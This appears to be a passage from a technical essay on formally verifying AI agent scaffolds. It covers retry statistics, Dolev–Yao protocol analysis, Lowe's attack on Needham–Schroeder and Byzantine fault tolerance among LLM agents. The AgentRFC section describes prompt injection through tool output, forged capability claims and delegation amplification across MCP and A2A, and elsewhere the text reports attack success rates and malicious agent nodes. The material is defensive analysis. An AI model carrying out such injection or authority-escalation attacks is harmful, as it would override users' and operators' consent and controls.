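Cui, Tang and colleagues (2026), in *RetryRoute*, give a formula for the cases in between. Let $q$ be the probability of success on a particular request, which may vary from one request to another, and let $p$ be its average. If attempts on the same request are independent, then after one failure the probability of success on the next try is

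$$\frac{E[q(1-q)]}{E[1-q]} = p - \frac{\text{Var}(q)}{1-p}.$$

A failure is evidence that the request is hard, so the next try is less likely to succeed whenever requests differ in difficulty. These three models have the same first-try rate:

| Requests | First try | Second try, after a failure | Within three tries |
|---|---|---|---|
| All succeed 80% of the time | 80% | 80% | 99.2% |
| Three quarters always succeed, the rest 20% of the time | 80% | 20% | 87.2% |
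| Four fifths always succeed, the rest never | 80% | 0% | 80% |

Recent measurements are far from the first row. Kelly, Kementsietsidis and colleagues (2026), in *Humanity's First Exam*, ran 18 models six times on each of 544 elementary questions, many of them about pictures. Ye, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *What Does a Repair Agent Gain from Remembering Its Failure?*, had agents fix real bugs in Python programs and retried every failed attempt from scratch. The table compares some of their results with what the formula for independent tries predicts:

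| Model and task | Tries | First-try success | Predicted | Observed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6.2 Astra, elementary questions | 4 | 97.8% | almost 100% | 97.9% |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite, elementary questions | 4 | 68.7% | 99.0% | 83.6% |
| gpt-5.4-mini, Python bugs | 2 | 59.7% | 83.7% | 71.7% |

For the strongest model, three extra tries gained a tenth of a percentage point. Kelly and colleagues kept only questions that at least one model had already failed, so failures that persist across retries may be more common in their test than in ordinary use. Ye and colleagues, who did not select tasks this way, found that a plain retry fixed 54 of 181 failures. They also found that 63 were not fixed by any of the five retries, four of which included information about the failed attempt.

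Cui and colleagues found the same pattern in image editing. Across six models, a retry after a failure succeeded only 17–53% as often as a first try. Within eight tries, the cheapest model succeeded on 80.4% of one benchmark, but it would have succeeded on almost 100% if the tries were independent. *When Can LLM Reasoning Reliably Reuse Intermediate Results?* (2026) tested models on arithmetic and found that some problems were still unsolved after 32 attempts in 85 of 320 test conditions.

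### When a retry helps

Whether another call will succeed depends heavily on what caused the failure. *CausalDS* (2026), a benchmark of data analysis, ran each task three times. Mistakes in data science recurred on all three runs 51.9% of the time, mistakes in reasoning 35.6%, and tool and runtime errors only 8.3%. It is therefore much more credible that one call in three will get past a temporary tool failure than that one in three will correct a misunderstanding.

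How often replies are malformed depends on the model. On one group of tasks in *UnpredictaBench* (2026), 68.6% of calls to Llama-3.2-1B needed a retry because the output was invalid, while calls to GPT-5.4 almost never did.

A scaffold can also change the prompt between tries, most simply by adding the error message. This worked well in *3DCodeBench* (2026), where models write programs that build 3D objects. About 90% of the initial failures came from using the wrong version of a software interface, and the error message showed what to fix. In Ye and colleagues' study, giving gpt-5.4-mini a transcript of its failed attempt raised the number of failures it fixed from 54 to 71 of 181, but the difference was not statistically significant.

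Feedback does not help a model that lacks the required ability. *Harness Engineering as Categorical Architecture* (2026) reports that retries with specific error messages fixed none of 30 submissions from a small model, which mostly failed to produce a code change in the right format. Small models may also repeat a call that has just failed, and *Feedback That Backfires* (2026) found that telling them in words not to repeat it did not solve the problem.

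Switching models after a failure can help more than retrying the same one. When FLUX.2 [klein], the cheapest image editor in one of Cui and colleagues' groups, retried edits it had just failed, it succeeded on 15% of them, while another model succeeded on 45%. The second model still did worse on those edits than on edits in general, so the two models' failures were not independent.

Retries also make reports of success less reliable. In Cui and colleagues' tests, a second automatic judge agreed with 84–93% of first-try passes, but with only 51–75% of passes that followed a failure. Hard requests produce many bad results, and a fallible judge eventually passes one.

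All these figures come from benchmark tasks. A hostile customer might write a complaint that makes every reply unusable, and for that complaint strong fairness and the bounded assumption would both be false.

The shop can instead prove a weaker form of completion without assuming anything about the model. It can prove that after at most three calls, either the customer has received a reply that passed the validator or the case is in a queue for staff. The proof needs only the call counter, the validator and a queue that stores what it receives. Proving that somebody then deals with the case requires a fairness assumption about the staff, which the shop can support by setting a deadline and checking the queue.

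## How does cryptographic protocol verification limit its arbitrary attacker?

Suppose the shop allows refunds above 100 if a manager approves them. To approve a refund, the manager gives the customer a secret code, and the agent pays only if the model's reply contains this code. With `havoc r` in place of the model, we cannot prove that large refunds need approval, because `r` can contain the right code even if the opponent has never seen it.

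Researchers who verify cryptographic protocols had to solve this problem early. Such a protocol is a fixed exchange of messages that uses encryption, for example to let two computers confirm each other's identity. If the attacker could send any string, it could send the secret keys, and no protocol would be secure. Researchers therefore usually assume that the attacker can act in any way, but can send only messages it can build from what it knows.

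### The Dolev–Yao attacker

*On the Security of Public Key Protocols* (Dolev and Yao, 1983) describes a "saboteur" who can read, alter and replay every message on the network. The saboteur is also a legitimate user, so it can start conversations with other users, and they can start conversations with it. Anyone can encrypt a message with a user's public key, but only that user has the private key that decrypts it. The paper assumes that nobody can break the encryption. *Verifying cryptographic protocols, I* (Paulson, 2022) defends this assumption, arguing that no protocol could be secure without it and that the aim is to find attacks that bypass encryption.

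Here $\{M\}_B$ denotes a message $M$ encrypted with Bob's public key. In Dolev and Yao's first example, Alice sends Bob her name and $\{M\}_B$, and Bob confirms receipt by returning $\{M\}_A$. The saboteur Z intercepts Alice's message, replaces her name with its own and forwards the message to Bob. Bob then returns $\{M\}_Z$, which Z can decrypt. Putting the sender's name inside the encryption, as in $\{M, A\}_B$, prevents this attack.

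An extra layer of encryption makes the repaired protocol insecure again. Alice now sends $\{\{M\}_B, A\}_B$ and Bob answers $\{\{M\}_A, B\}_A$. Z can use Bob's answer as the inner part of a new message to Alice. She removes both layers and returns the contents encrypted for Z, which gives Z $\{M\}_A$. Z sends this to Alice in another message and decrypts her answer to get $M$.

Dolev and Yao's protocols only add names and layers of encryption. Cortier and Kremer (2017), in *Formal Models and Techniques for Analyzing Security Protocols*, give the more general rules now in use. Write $K \vdash m$ if the attacker can build $m$ from a set of messages $K$, and $k^{-1}$ for the key that decrypts what $k$ encrypts:

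| Operation | If the attacker has | it can build |
|---|---|---|
| Use a known message | $m$ in $K$ | $m$ |
| Pair | $m$ and $m'$ | $(m, m')$ |
| Split | $(m, m')$ | $m$ and $m'$ |
| Encrypt | $m$ and $k$ | $\{m\}_k$ |
| Decrypt | $\{m\}_k$ and $k^{-1}$ | $m$ |

Suppose the attacker has seen $(k_1, k_2)$, $(k_3, a)$ and the number $n$ encrypted with the pair $(k_1, k_3)$, where the same key encrypts and decrypts. It can split the first two messages to get $k_1$ and $k_3$, pair them and decrypt $n$.

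These rules generate infinitely many messages, because the attacker can keep pairing and encrypting. But Cortier and Kremer prove that if $m$ is derivable, some derivation uses only parts of $m$ and parts of messages in $K$. An algorithm can therefore collect the derivable parts in polynomial time, stopping when it finds no more.

### Lowe's attack

The Needham–Schroeder public-key protocol dates from 1978. It uses nonces, which are random numbers that each serve for a single session. Alice creates $N_a$ and Bob creates $N_b$:

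1. Alice to Bob: $\{N_a, A\}_B$
2. Bob to Alice: $\{N_a, N_b\}_A$
3. Alice to Bob: $\{N_b\}_B$

Only Bob can decrypt the first message, so when $N_a$ comes back, Alice concludes that she is talking to Bob. When $N_b$ comes back, Bob likewise concludes that he is talking to Alice.

Lowe, in *Breaking and Fixing the Needham-Schroeder Public-Key Protocol Using FDR*, checked this with a model checker called FDR. The model contained Alice, Bob and the most general intruder, whose state records only what it has learned. FDR searched for a run in which Bob completes a session with Alice although she never started one with him. It found one that begins when Alice contacts the intruder, I, as an ordinary user:

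| Step | Message | What the intruder does |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Alice to I: $\{N_a, A\}_I$ | Decrypts it and learns $N_a$ |
| 2 | I to Bob, posing as Alice: $\{N_a, A\}_B$ | Encrypts the same contents for Bob |
| 3 | Bob to Alice: $\{N_a, N_b\}_A$ | Intercepts it but cannot read it |
| 4 | I to Alice: $\{N_a, N_b\}_A$ | Forwards it unchanged |
| 5 | Alice to I: $\{N_b\}_I$ | Decrypts it and learns $N_b$ |
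| 6 | I to Bob, posing as Alice: $\{N_b\}_B$ | Completes the session |

Alice decrypts $N_b$ for the intruder because the message in step 4 has the form she expects. The protocol had been public for 17 years before anyone broke it, and an earlier paper had presented a proof that it was correct.

Lowe's repair adds Bob's name to the second message, making it $\{N_a, N_b, B\}_A$. Alice expects the intruder's name in step 4, so she rejects the message. FDR found no attack on the repaired protocol when Alice and Bob each took part in one session. Lowe then proved by hand that any attack on a larger system would imply an attack on this small one.

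Cortier and Kremer say it is debatable whether Lowe's finding counts as an attack, because Needham and Schroeder had assumed that users choose to communicate securely. They add that malware and phishing have since made that assumption unreasonable.

### Proving that a refund needs the code

Here is the part of the agent that handles refunds above 100:

```
havoc r                        # the model call
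if r = Large(x, c):
    if c = code:
        assert released        # a manager has given out the code
        pay(x)
history := history + r
```

The scaffold creates a new `code` for each complaint. The variable `released` exists only for the proof and becomes true when the manager gives the code to the customer. By the `havoc` rule, the assertion requires

$$\forall x, c.\ (c = code \Rightarrow released).$$

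One of the values of $c$ is `code`, so this reduces to `released`. At the start `released` is false, and the proof fails.

To apply the derivability rule, let $K$ contain everything the opponent can read, including the whole prompt, and add an assumption after the call:

```
havoc r
assume K ⊢ r
```

An opponent that can build the pair $(x, c)$ can also split it and obtain $c$. The condition therefore becomes

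$$K \vdash code\ \Rightarrow\ released,$$

or in words, the opponent can build the code only after a manager has released it. This follows from the invariant "until the code is released, no message in $K$ contains it", where "contains" includes text inside an encryption. We prove the invariant in three steps:

- The code is new, so at the start no message in $K$ contains it.
- If no message in $K$ contains the code, neither does any message derivable from $K$. Splitting and decrypting only return parts of existing messages. Pairing and encrypting combine messages without the code, and cannot create it because the rules treat it as a single indivisible value.
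- The reply therefore doesn't contain the code, the test `c = code` fails, and adding the reply to `history` preserves the invariant.

The argument works for any number of calls, but only if the code stays out of the prompt. If the scaffold answers a wrong guess with "expected 7291, got 0000" and adds this message to `history`, the invariant becomes false and the next reply can contain the right code. The same happens if the manager emails the code to a mailbox that the agent can read.

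### The price of assuming that nobody guesses

No validator can enforce `assume K ⊢ r`, because a guessed code looks exactly like one the model has read. The assumption needs support from probability. Suppose the scaffold draws the code uniformly from $N$ values and uses it only in the comparison. Fix a strategy for the opponent that doesn't depend on the code. As long as its guesses are wrong, the scaffold behaves the same way whatever the code is, so the strategy produces the same three guesses $g_1, g_2, g_3$. It succeeds only if the code is among them, so

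$$P(\text{success}) \leq \frac{3}{N}.$$

The bound also holds for a model that samples its replies, because sampling amounts to choosing a strategy at random. Plain `havoc` fails here, as in the coin-flip example, because it lets the opponent choose after seeing the result.

With a four-digit code, the bound is 3 in 10,000. If attackers tried this on a million complaints, they could expect up to 300 unapproved refunds. With 128 random bits, the bound is about $10^{-38}$. The limit of three calls now matters for safety as well as for halting, because an attacker with unlimited calls could try all 10,000 four-digit codes.

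Encryption needs a more elaborate justification, because real ciphertexts are strings of bits that an attacker can manipulate in ways the rules may not cover. Backes, Pfitzmann and Waidner (2008) built an idealised cryptographic library that researchers can use in proofs as they would the Dolev–Yao model, and an implementation of it that is provably secure under active attacks. They used the library to show that Lowe's repaired protocol is secure when implemented with standard, provably secure cryptography.

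A proof can still miss attacks if the rules omit something the real operations allow. Cortier and Kremer give the example of encryption that processes a long message in blocks. With some methods, an attacker without the key can cut off the end of the ciphertext and obtain a valid encryption of the beginning of the message. The table above has no rule for this, so a system that uses such a method needs an extra rule.

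### Long runs and many sessions

A person supplied the invariant for the approval code. Searching for attacks automatically becomes much harder as the number of sessions grows. *Protocol insecurity with a finite number of sessions, composed keys is NP-complete* proves that deciding whether an attack exists is NP-complete for a fixed number of sessions, with no limit on message size. The search is still finite because an attacker who can succeed needs only messages of linear size, counting repeated parts once.

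Whether a protocol leaks a secret is undecidable if the protocol can run unlimited sessions and generate fresh values such as nonces. Liang and Verma prove one version of this by encoding two-counter machines as protocols. These machines can compute anything a computer can, so an algorithm that could always determine whether a secret leaks would also solve the halting problem.

The search is bounded for one complaint with three model calls. The undecidable class includes a permanent service that issues a new code for every complaint and a long-running agent that keeps creating credentials for other agents. A developer can limit the number of sessions, but then the proof covers only that many. Otherwise, the developer can prove an invariant, reduce the problem to a small system like Lowe's, or use a prover that may fail to find an answer.

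Wilson, Asplund and Johansson (2026) take the last route in *AutoTam*, using Tamarin, a prover that can cover any number of sessions but relies on heuristics. Their tool generates the Tamarin model from the program that runs, and they prove that properties of single runs carry over from the model to the program. Most earlier tools of this kind restricted loops, but AutoTam programs are state machines that may contain cycles, which an agent loop would also need. They used the tool to verify an implementation of WireGuard, a protocol for private network connections.

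### Robust safety

In the proofs so far, the opponent supplies messages. Gordon and Jeffrey (2002), in *Authenticity by Typing for Security Protocols*, represent it as a program that runs at the same time as the verified one. They call a program $P$ robustly safe if

$$P \parallel O \text{ is safe for every opponent program } O.$$

Both programs use the spi-calculus, a small language for communicating processes with built-in encryption. When $P$ creates a new key, $O$ cannot name that key until some process sends it. The language therefore enforces the rule about unguessable values without a separate assumption.

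Gordon and Jeffrey define safety by marking points in a program with `begin L` or `end L`, where `L` is a label. A run is safe if every `end L` has its own earlier `begin L`. The opponent may not use these markers, because an opponent consisting only of `end x` would otherwise make every program unsafe.

In the shop, the manager's approval could execute `begin(complaint, amount)` and the agent's payment `end(complaint, amount)`. Requiring each `end` to have its own matching `begin` reveals two faults in the agent above, although we proved that it never pays a large refund before the manager releases the code. If the manager approves 150, the model can request 5,000 with the same code, and no `begin` matches that payment. The model can also request 150 twice, and the second payment has no matching `begin` because the first already used it.

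Gordon and Jeffrey describe the second fault in a protocol where one participant sends encrypted messages to another. The attacker delivers a message twice, and the receiver accepts both copies because each is genuine. In the repaired protocol, the receiver first sends a fresh nonce, the sender includes it in the encrypted message, and the receiver accepts each nonce only once. Similarly, the shop can store the approved amount with the code and delete both before paying.

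Gordon and Jeffrey use a type checker instead of searching for attacks. It counts the `end` markers that have no matching `begin` and allows the program to check each nonce only once. All data that the opponent can touch has a special untrusted type. Any opponent program passes the checker if all its data has this type, so the method doesn't exclude any attackers. Gordon and Jeffrey prove that every protocol that passes is robustly safe, with no limit on the number of sessions or the size of the opponent. But the checker also rejects some correct protocols, including some that use nonces in other ways.

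Researchers later applied robust safety to machine code on capability machines, where a program can access memory only if it holds a capability for it. The opponent is arbitrary code on the same machine, and the hardware stops it from forging capabilities. This approach would suit a scaffold that runs code written by the model.

### AgentRFC

Agents often communicate through shared protocols. MCP, for example, connects an agent to servers that offer tools, and A2A lets one agent delegate tasks to another. Zheng and Zhang (2026), in *AgentRFC*, analysed five such protocols with a Dolev–Yao attacker that has three additional powers:

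- **Prompt injection:** it can put instructions into a tool's output.
- **Capability inflation:** it can forge or exaggerate the list of things that a tool or agent is able to do.
- **Delegation amplification:** it can pass on more authority than it received.

Maloyan and Namiot (2026) explain in *Breaking the Protocol* why the second power is realistic for MCP. A server declares its own capabilities, and the client cannot check the declaration.

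Zheng and Zhang extracted the rules from each protocol's documentation and turned them into TLA+ models. Every action in a model belongs to the protocol, the environment or the adversary. The environment's actions are harmless events, such as a credential expiring. A failing run therefore shows whether the fault needs an attacker or can occur in normal operation, which a single `havoc` would not show.

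The model checker TLC tested the protocols against 11 security principles and found 33 violations. Many occur because a protocol lacks a rule. For example, A2A doesn't limit what an agent may delegate, so its model violates the principle that agents delegate only what they have. Zheng and Zhang report a clearer fault in MCP. Its specification requires servers to sanitize tool outputs, but the reference software doesn't sanitize them.

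Zheng and Zhang also built five models of protocols working together, and 20 of the 21 properties they checked failed. In one pattern, an operation that needs the user's consent under one protocol goes through another protocol that has no consent step. In another, an injected instruction arrives through MCP, passes through a program that bridges MCP and A2A, and gives an A2A agent more authority than anyone granted it. They stress that analysing each protocol separately would not have revealed these violations, which is partly true by definition because the properties concern the connection between protocols.

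The models contain only two or three agents and two capabilities. A violation found in one is real for that model, but finding none doesn't prove that larger systems are free of violations, because there is no counterpart to Lowe's reduction. It is also unclear how many violations affect real software. The paper's introduction reports 42 tests that confirmed violations, but its discussion describes the testing as ongoing, with specific findings withheld.

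### Language has no deduction rules

Alice follows a fixed program, so a model checker can calculate her answer to any message the intruder builds. No comparable rule determines whether a language model will obey an instruction hidden in a complaint. Zheng and Zhang likewise describe the language model as a probabilistic parser. Their TLA+ models represent a successful injection as an action the adversary can take, without describing which texts would succeed.

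Authenticating messages doesn't fill this gap, because a signature proves who sent a text but not how the model will react to it. Maloyan and Namiot added signed capabilities, message authentication and isolation between servers to MCP. In tests with models from 2024, these changes cut the attack success rate from 52.8% to 12.4%.

Counting the language model as part of the attacker is the safe choice for a proof, because nobody then has to predict which instructions the model will follow. The approval-code proof did this by putting the whole prompt into $K$.

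The rules can still give the wrong answer about what a text reveals, because they only determine whether the opponent can build the code, and ordinary language can narrow down a secret without containing it. If the prompt says "the code is the manager's year of birth", the symbolic proof succeeds, although fewer than a hundred codes are plausible. A similar problem arises with a hash of a four-digit code, which is a scrambled version that is hard to reverse. The rules give no way to undo the hash, but an attacker can hash all 10,000 codes and see which one matches.

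Cortier and Kremer discuss a related difficulty with secret ballots. The possible votes, 0 and 1, are public, so they ask whether the attacker can tell one vote from the other by comparing messages, rather than whether the attacker can derive them. This test covers the hash if the analysis compares two possible codes that the attacker knows, but it doesn't cover hints in English. To rule those out, the shop has to keep everything in the prompt independent of the code, by drawing the code at random and using it only in the comparison until a manager releases it.

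## What does Byzantine fault tolerance show about arbitrary failures?

Byzantine fault tolerance, like a cryptographic proof, allows arbitrary behavior, but it limits how many participants can be faulty rather than what an attacker knows. Suppose the shop runs its scaffold on several computers so that refunds continue if one fails. Each computer keeps its own copy of `paid`, and the copies stay equal only if the computers agree on every request. A faulty computer may report a refund of 60 to one computer and no refund to another.

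*The Byzantine Generals Problem* (Lamport, Shostak and Pease, 1982) describes such computers as generals camped around a city, who communicate by messenger. A commander sends an order to the other generals, called lieutenants. Some of the generals, possibly including the commander, are traitors and may send anything, including different messages to different people. The loyal generals follow a fixed procedure, which must guarantee two conditions:

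- **Agreement:** all loyal lieutenants obey the same order.
- **Validity:** if the commander is loyal, every loyal lieutenant obeys the order that the commander sent.

### Why three generals are not enough

Suppose there are three generals, one of whom may be a traitor, and the order is either "attack" or "retreat". No procedure can guarantee both conditions:

1. Suppose the commander is loyal and orders both lieutenants to attack. Lieutenant 2 is a traitor and tells Lieutenant 1 that the order was to retreat. By validity, Lieutenant 1 must attack.
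2. Now suppose the commander is the traitor, and orders Lieutenant 1 to attack and Lieutenant 2 to retreat. Lieutenant 2 truthfully reports an order to retreat. Lieutenant 1 receives the same messages as before, so Lieutenant 1 attacks again.
3. By the same argument with the orders exchanged, a lieutenant whom the commander tells to retreat must retreat, whatever the other lieutenant reports. So Lieutenant 2 retreats.
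4. Both lieutenants are loyal in this second situation, but one attacks and the other retreats, which violates agreement.

Sending more messages doesn't help, because the traitor can keep up the lie. Lamport and colleagues warn that informal arguments about such procedures often go wrong, and refer readers to a rigorous proof in their earlier paper, *Reaching Agreement in the Presence of Faults*. Lamport recalls that before that paper, people generally assumed three computers could tolerate one faulty one.

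The result extends to larger groups. Suppose some procedure let $3f$ generals cope with $f$ traitors. Three generals could then use it, with each playing the parts of $f$ generals. One traitor among the three would account for at most $f$ traitors in the larger group, so the three could cope with one traitor, which is impossible. Coping with $f$ traitors therefore takes at least $3f+1$ generals.

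Four generals can still agree on a plan if one of them is a traitor. Each lieutenant forwards the commander's order to the other two, then follows the majority of the three orders received, or retreats if there is no majority. If one lieutenant is a traitor, the other two still each have two correct copies out of three. If the commander is the traitor, all three lieutenants are loyal, so they receive the same three orders and make the same choice.

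Signatures that nobody can forge remove the ambiguity in the three-general argument. Lieutenant 2 can no longer invent an order to retreat, because the order would need the commander's signature. If the commander signs two different orders, the lieutenants exchange them, see that the commander is a traitor and both retreat. With signatures, agreement is possible for any number of traitors. If the group takes a majority vote, loyal members must still outnumber the $f$ traitors, which requires at least $2f+1$ members.

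### Agreement always, progress when messages arrive on time

These procedures assume that a general can tell when a message is missing, which requires a known limit on delivery times. On the internet, a slow computer can look exactly like a crashed one. *Consensus in the Presence of Partial Synchrony* (Dwork, Lynch and Stockmeyer, 1988) therefore uses a weaker assumption. Messages may be late or lost at first, but from some moment on, unknown to the computers, they arrive within a fixed time.

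In protocols for this setting, correct computers never make conflicting decisions, but they are certain to reach a decision only once messages arrive on time. The first guarantee holds even if the timing never improves. If two correct computers made conflicting decisions, they would do so at some finite moment, and the timing could still become good afterwards. The protocol would then have failed in a run that it was supposed to handle. Similarly, the refund agent's cap holds for every model, but a proof that the agent answers the customer requires a fairness assumption.

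Signatures no longer reduce the number of computers needed in this setting. Castro and Liskov (1999), in *Practical Byzantine Fault Tolerance*, explain why $3f+1$ are necessary. With $n$ computers, of which $f$ may be faulty, a computer can wait for only $n-f$ replies, because the faulty ones may never answer. But the silent computers may be correct and merely slow, in which case $f$ of the replies come from faulty computers. The correct replies must outnumber the faulty ones, so

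$$n - 2f > f, \qquad \text{or} \qquad n > 3f.$$

### Where the model fits in

Castro and Liskov require every correct computer to be deterministic, so that the same request in the same state always gives the same result. A language model that samples its replies breaks this rule. If each of the shop's computers called the model itself, one might receive `Refund(60)` and another `Refund(50)`, even though neither computer is faulty. The shop can instead call the model once and have the computers agree on the reply, as they would on any other input.

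Agreement among the computers doesn't make the model's reply correct. Lamport and colleagues point out that a faulty input device may supply meaningless values, and that their procedures ensure only that all the computers use the same value. If the model returns `Refund(5000)`, every correct computer will process that value, and the guard still has to block it.

The model is in the same position as a client in Castro and Liskov's system, where any number of clients may be faulty. If every operation of the service preserves an invariant, faulty clients cannot break it. So the refund cap holds however many models are faulty, as long as the number of faulty computers stays within a limit.

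The shop needs to assume a limit on the number of faulty models only if it relies on their judgment. Suppose four agents vote on whether a customer deserves a refund, and one trusted scaffold counts the votes. No agent can send different votes to different recipients, so the generals' problem doesn't arise. But the result is reliable only if few enough agents are wrong, and that assumption about the models needs support.

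### Copies that fail together

Castro and Liskov explicitly assume that computers fail independently. To make this assumption credible under attack, they recommend that each computer run a different implementation of the service and a different operating system, and have its own administrator and root password.

Four copies of one model reading the same complaint have no such separation. In the extreme case, either all four judge the complaint correctly or all four get it wrong, so an attacker who finds a complaint that fools one copy has fooled them all. The classical bound lets four participants tolerate one fault, which doesn't help when the number of faults is always zero or four. Suppose each copy misjudges 1% of complaints. If the errors were independent, two or more copies would misjudge the same complaint only about 0.06% of the time. If the copies always fail together, all four misjudge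 1% of complaints, the same rate as a single copy.

He and Yu (2026), in *The Honest Quorum Problem*, extend the classical bound. Besides the $f$ Byzantine agents, they allow for up to $e$ agents that follow the voting protocol correctly but approve the same bad action by mistake. Here $e$ is a statistical bound, which the true number may exceed with some small probability. Within that bound, a bad action can collect up to $f+e$ approvals, so the system must require more than $f+e$. For identical copies that fail together, $e$ may be as large as $n-f$. The system would then need more than $n$ approvals from $n$ agents, which is impossible.

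Different models can still fail together if they share evidence. In *The Illusion of Independent Quorums* (2026), He and Yu count the smallest number of separate causes that could mislead enough voters to approve an action. If three of five reviewers read the same outdated data and three approvals are enough, that number is one. They prove that adding voters without raising the threshold can never increase this number. In the shop, one forged receipt can mislead three different models that all read it. Having one of them check the courier's delivery record instead would add separate evidence. He and Yu support their method with proofs and simulations, not with tests on real models.

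Some systems simply assume a limit on how many agents are faulty. In *Byzantine-Robust Decentralized Coordination of LLM Agents*, Jo and Park (2025) have one group of agents write answers and another group score them. They assume that a majority of each group is honest, and combine the scores in a way that tolerates a minority of dishonest evaluators. This protects against evaluators that collude, but not against an answer that misleads all the honest evaluators.

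### How often do different models make the same mistake?

Different models do share errors. *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026) tested models on multiple-choice questions and found that when models got a question wrong, they chose the same wrong option 87% of the time on average. A majority vote among 15 models was right on 84.3% of questions, while the best single model scored 90.5%. For 98.4% of the questions, at least one model chose the right answer, but it was often outvoted.

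Better models may make this problem worse. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that errors were more correlated among accurate models, and among models that shared a developer or base architecture.

Programs written by coding agents also fail together. *N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (2026) compared 48 programs written to one specification and found 429 coincident failures, when independence would predict about 115. Knight and Leveson had found much the same with human programmers. Voting still helped. A single program failed 387 times on average, while a group of three that voted failed 131 times, and 68% of the possible groups of three never failed in the tests. Redundancy can therefore be useful even when errors are too correlated to justify assuming a limit on the number of simultaneous faults.

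### Can language-model agents reach agreement?

In the classical protocols, the correct participants run a fixed program. *Can AI Agents Agree?* (Berdoz, Rugli and Wattenhofer, 2026) tested whether language models could reach agreement by discussion. Each agent started with a random number from 0 to 50. In every round, the agents sent one another a proposed number with a justification, then voted on whether to stop. A run succeeded if two thirds of the agents voted to stop within 50 rounds and all the honest agents held the same number, which one of them had started with.

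Of 600 runs without any Byzantine agents, 41.6% succeeded. Qwen3-14B succeeded in 67.4% of its runs and the smaller Qwen3-8B in 15.8%. Groups of four agents succeeded in 46.6% of runs and groups of 16 in 33.3%. Merely mentioning that Byzantine agents might exist lowered Qwen3-14B's success rate from 75.4% to 59.1%. Most failures were timeouts.

An ordinary program would solve this version of the task in one round by having every agent send its number and adopt the smallest. The poor results therefore come from the models' difficulty in coordinating, not from a theoretical limit. A designer who needs agreement should put the protocol in the scaffold and have the models supply only the values.

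Berdoz and colleagues then added one to four Byzantine agents to eight honest ones. Success became much rarer, again mainly because of timeouts, even though the Byzantine agents could not send different messages to different recipients. Agreement on a wrong number remained rare, but no protocol could have ruled it out, because if all the starting numbers differ, a Byzantine agent can behave exactly like an honest one and the group may settle on its number.

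### Results that seem to beat the bound

*Rethinking the Reliability of Multi-agent System* (Zheng, Chen and colleagues, 2025) reports that language-model agents can tolerate six malicious nodes out of seven, far more than a third. In the first experiment, the honest node was GPT-4o-mini and the six "malicious" nodes were GPT-3.5-turbo, a weaker model, with the same ordinary prompts. The group answered ten school maths problems, chosen because strong models tend to solve them and weak ones often don't. When all the nodes could communicate with each other, the group got nine of the ten right.

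These malicious nodes were often correct. Before any communication, 62.9% of the nodes' answers were right, or 4.4 of the seven nodes on average. Only one node was honest, so on average at least 3.4 of the six malicious nodes were right. A Byzantine node in the classical sense could have given whatever answer did the most damage.

Zheng and colleagues also built a system that gives more weight to nodes with higher confidence. Lee, Yun and colleagues (2026), in *Robust Multi-Agent LLMs under Byzantine Faults*, tested it against adversaries that gave wrong answers and falsely reported a confidence of 1.0. They compared it with their own method, in which each agent scores the answers it receives, discards up to three that score lower than its own, and then revises its answer. The agents repeat this for six rounds. The table shows how often the majority of honest agents ended up with the right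 answer, in groups of seven where every agent could communicate with every other:

| Problems | Strongest model in the group | Adversaries | Reported confidence | Agents' own scores |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| MATH, 100 problems | GPT-4o-mini | 1 | 49.0% | 78.0% |
| AIME 2025 | Qwen3-4B-Thinking | 1 | 0.0% | 76.7% |
| HMMT-25 | GPT-5.6-sol | 3 | 10.0% | 93.3% |

The classical bound allows two traitors in a group of seven, but the confidence-based system did badly with one adversary that misreported its confidence. The groups with one adversary also contained two weaker honest models.

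In the HMMT-25 test, Lee and colleagues' method did well with more than a third of the agents (three of seven) acting as adversaries. But the four honest agents had each solved every problem before communicating, so a simple majority vote on the initial answers would have scored 100%. Discussion lowered the agents' accuracy. The method also depends on agents recognizing correct answers, and Lee and colleagues acknowledge that an overconfident agent may discard them.

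None of these results contradicts Lamport and colleagues' proof that for every procedure with at most $3f$ participants, *some* behavior of $f$ traitors defeats it. An experiment measures how often a procedure succeeds against the behavior the researchers chose, and Lee and colleagues tested only one kind of adversary. The tasks also differ, because an honest agent can solve a maths problem without help and ignore everyone else, but a lieutenant cannot work out by reasoning which order the commander sent to the others.
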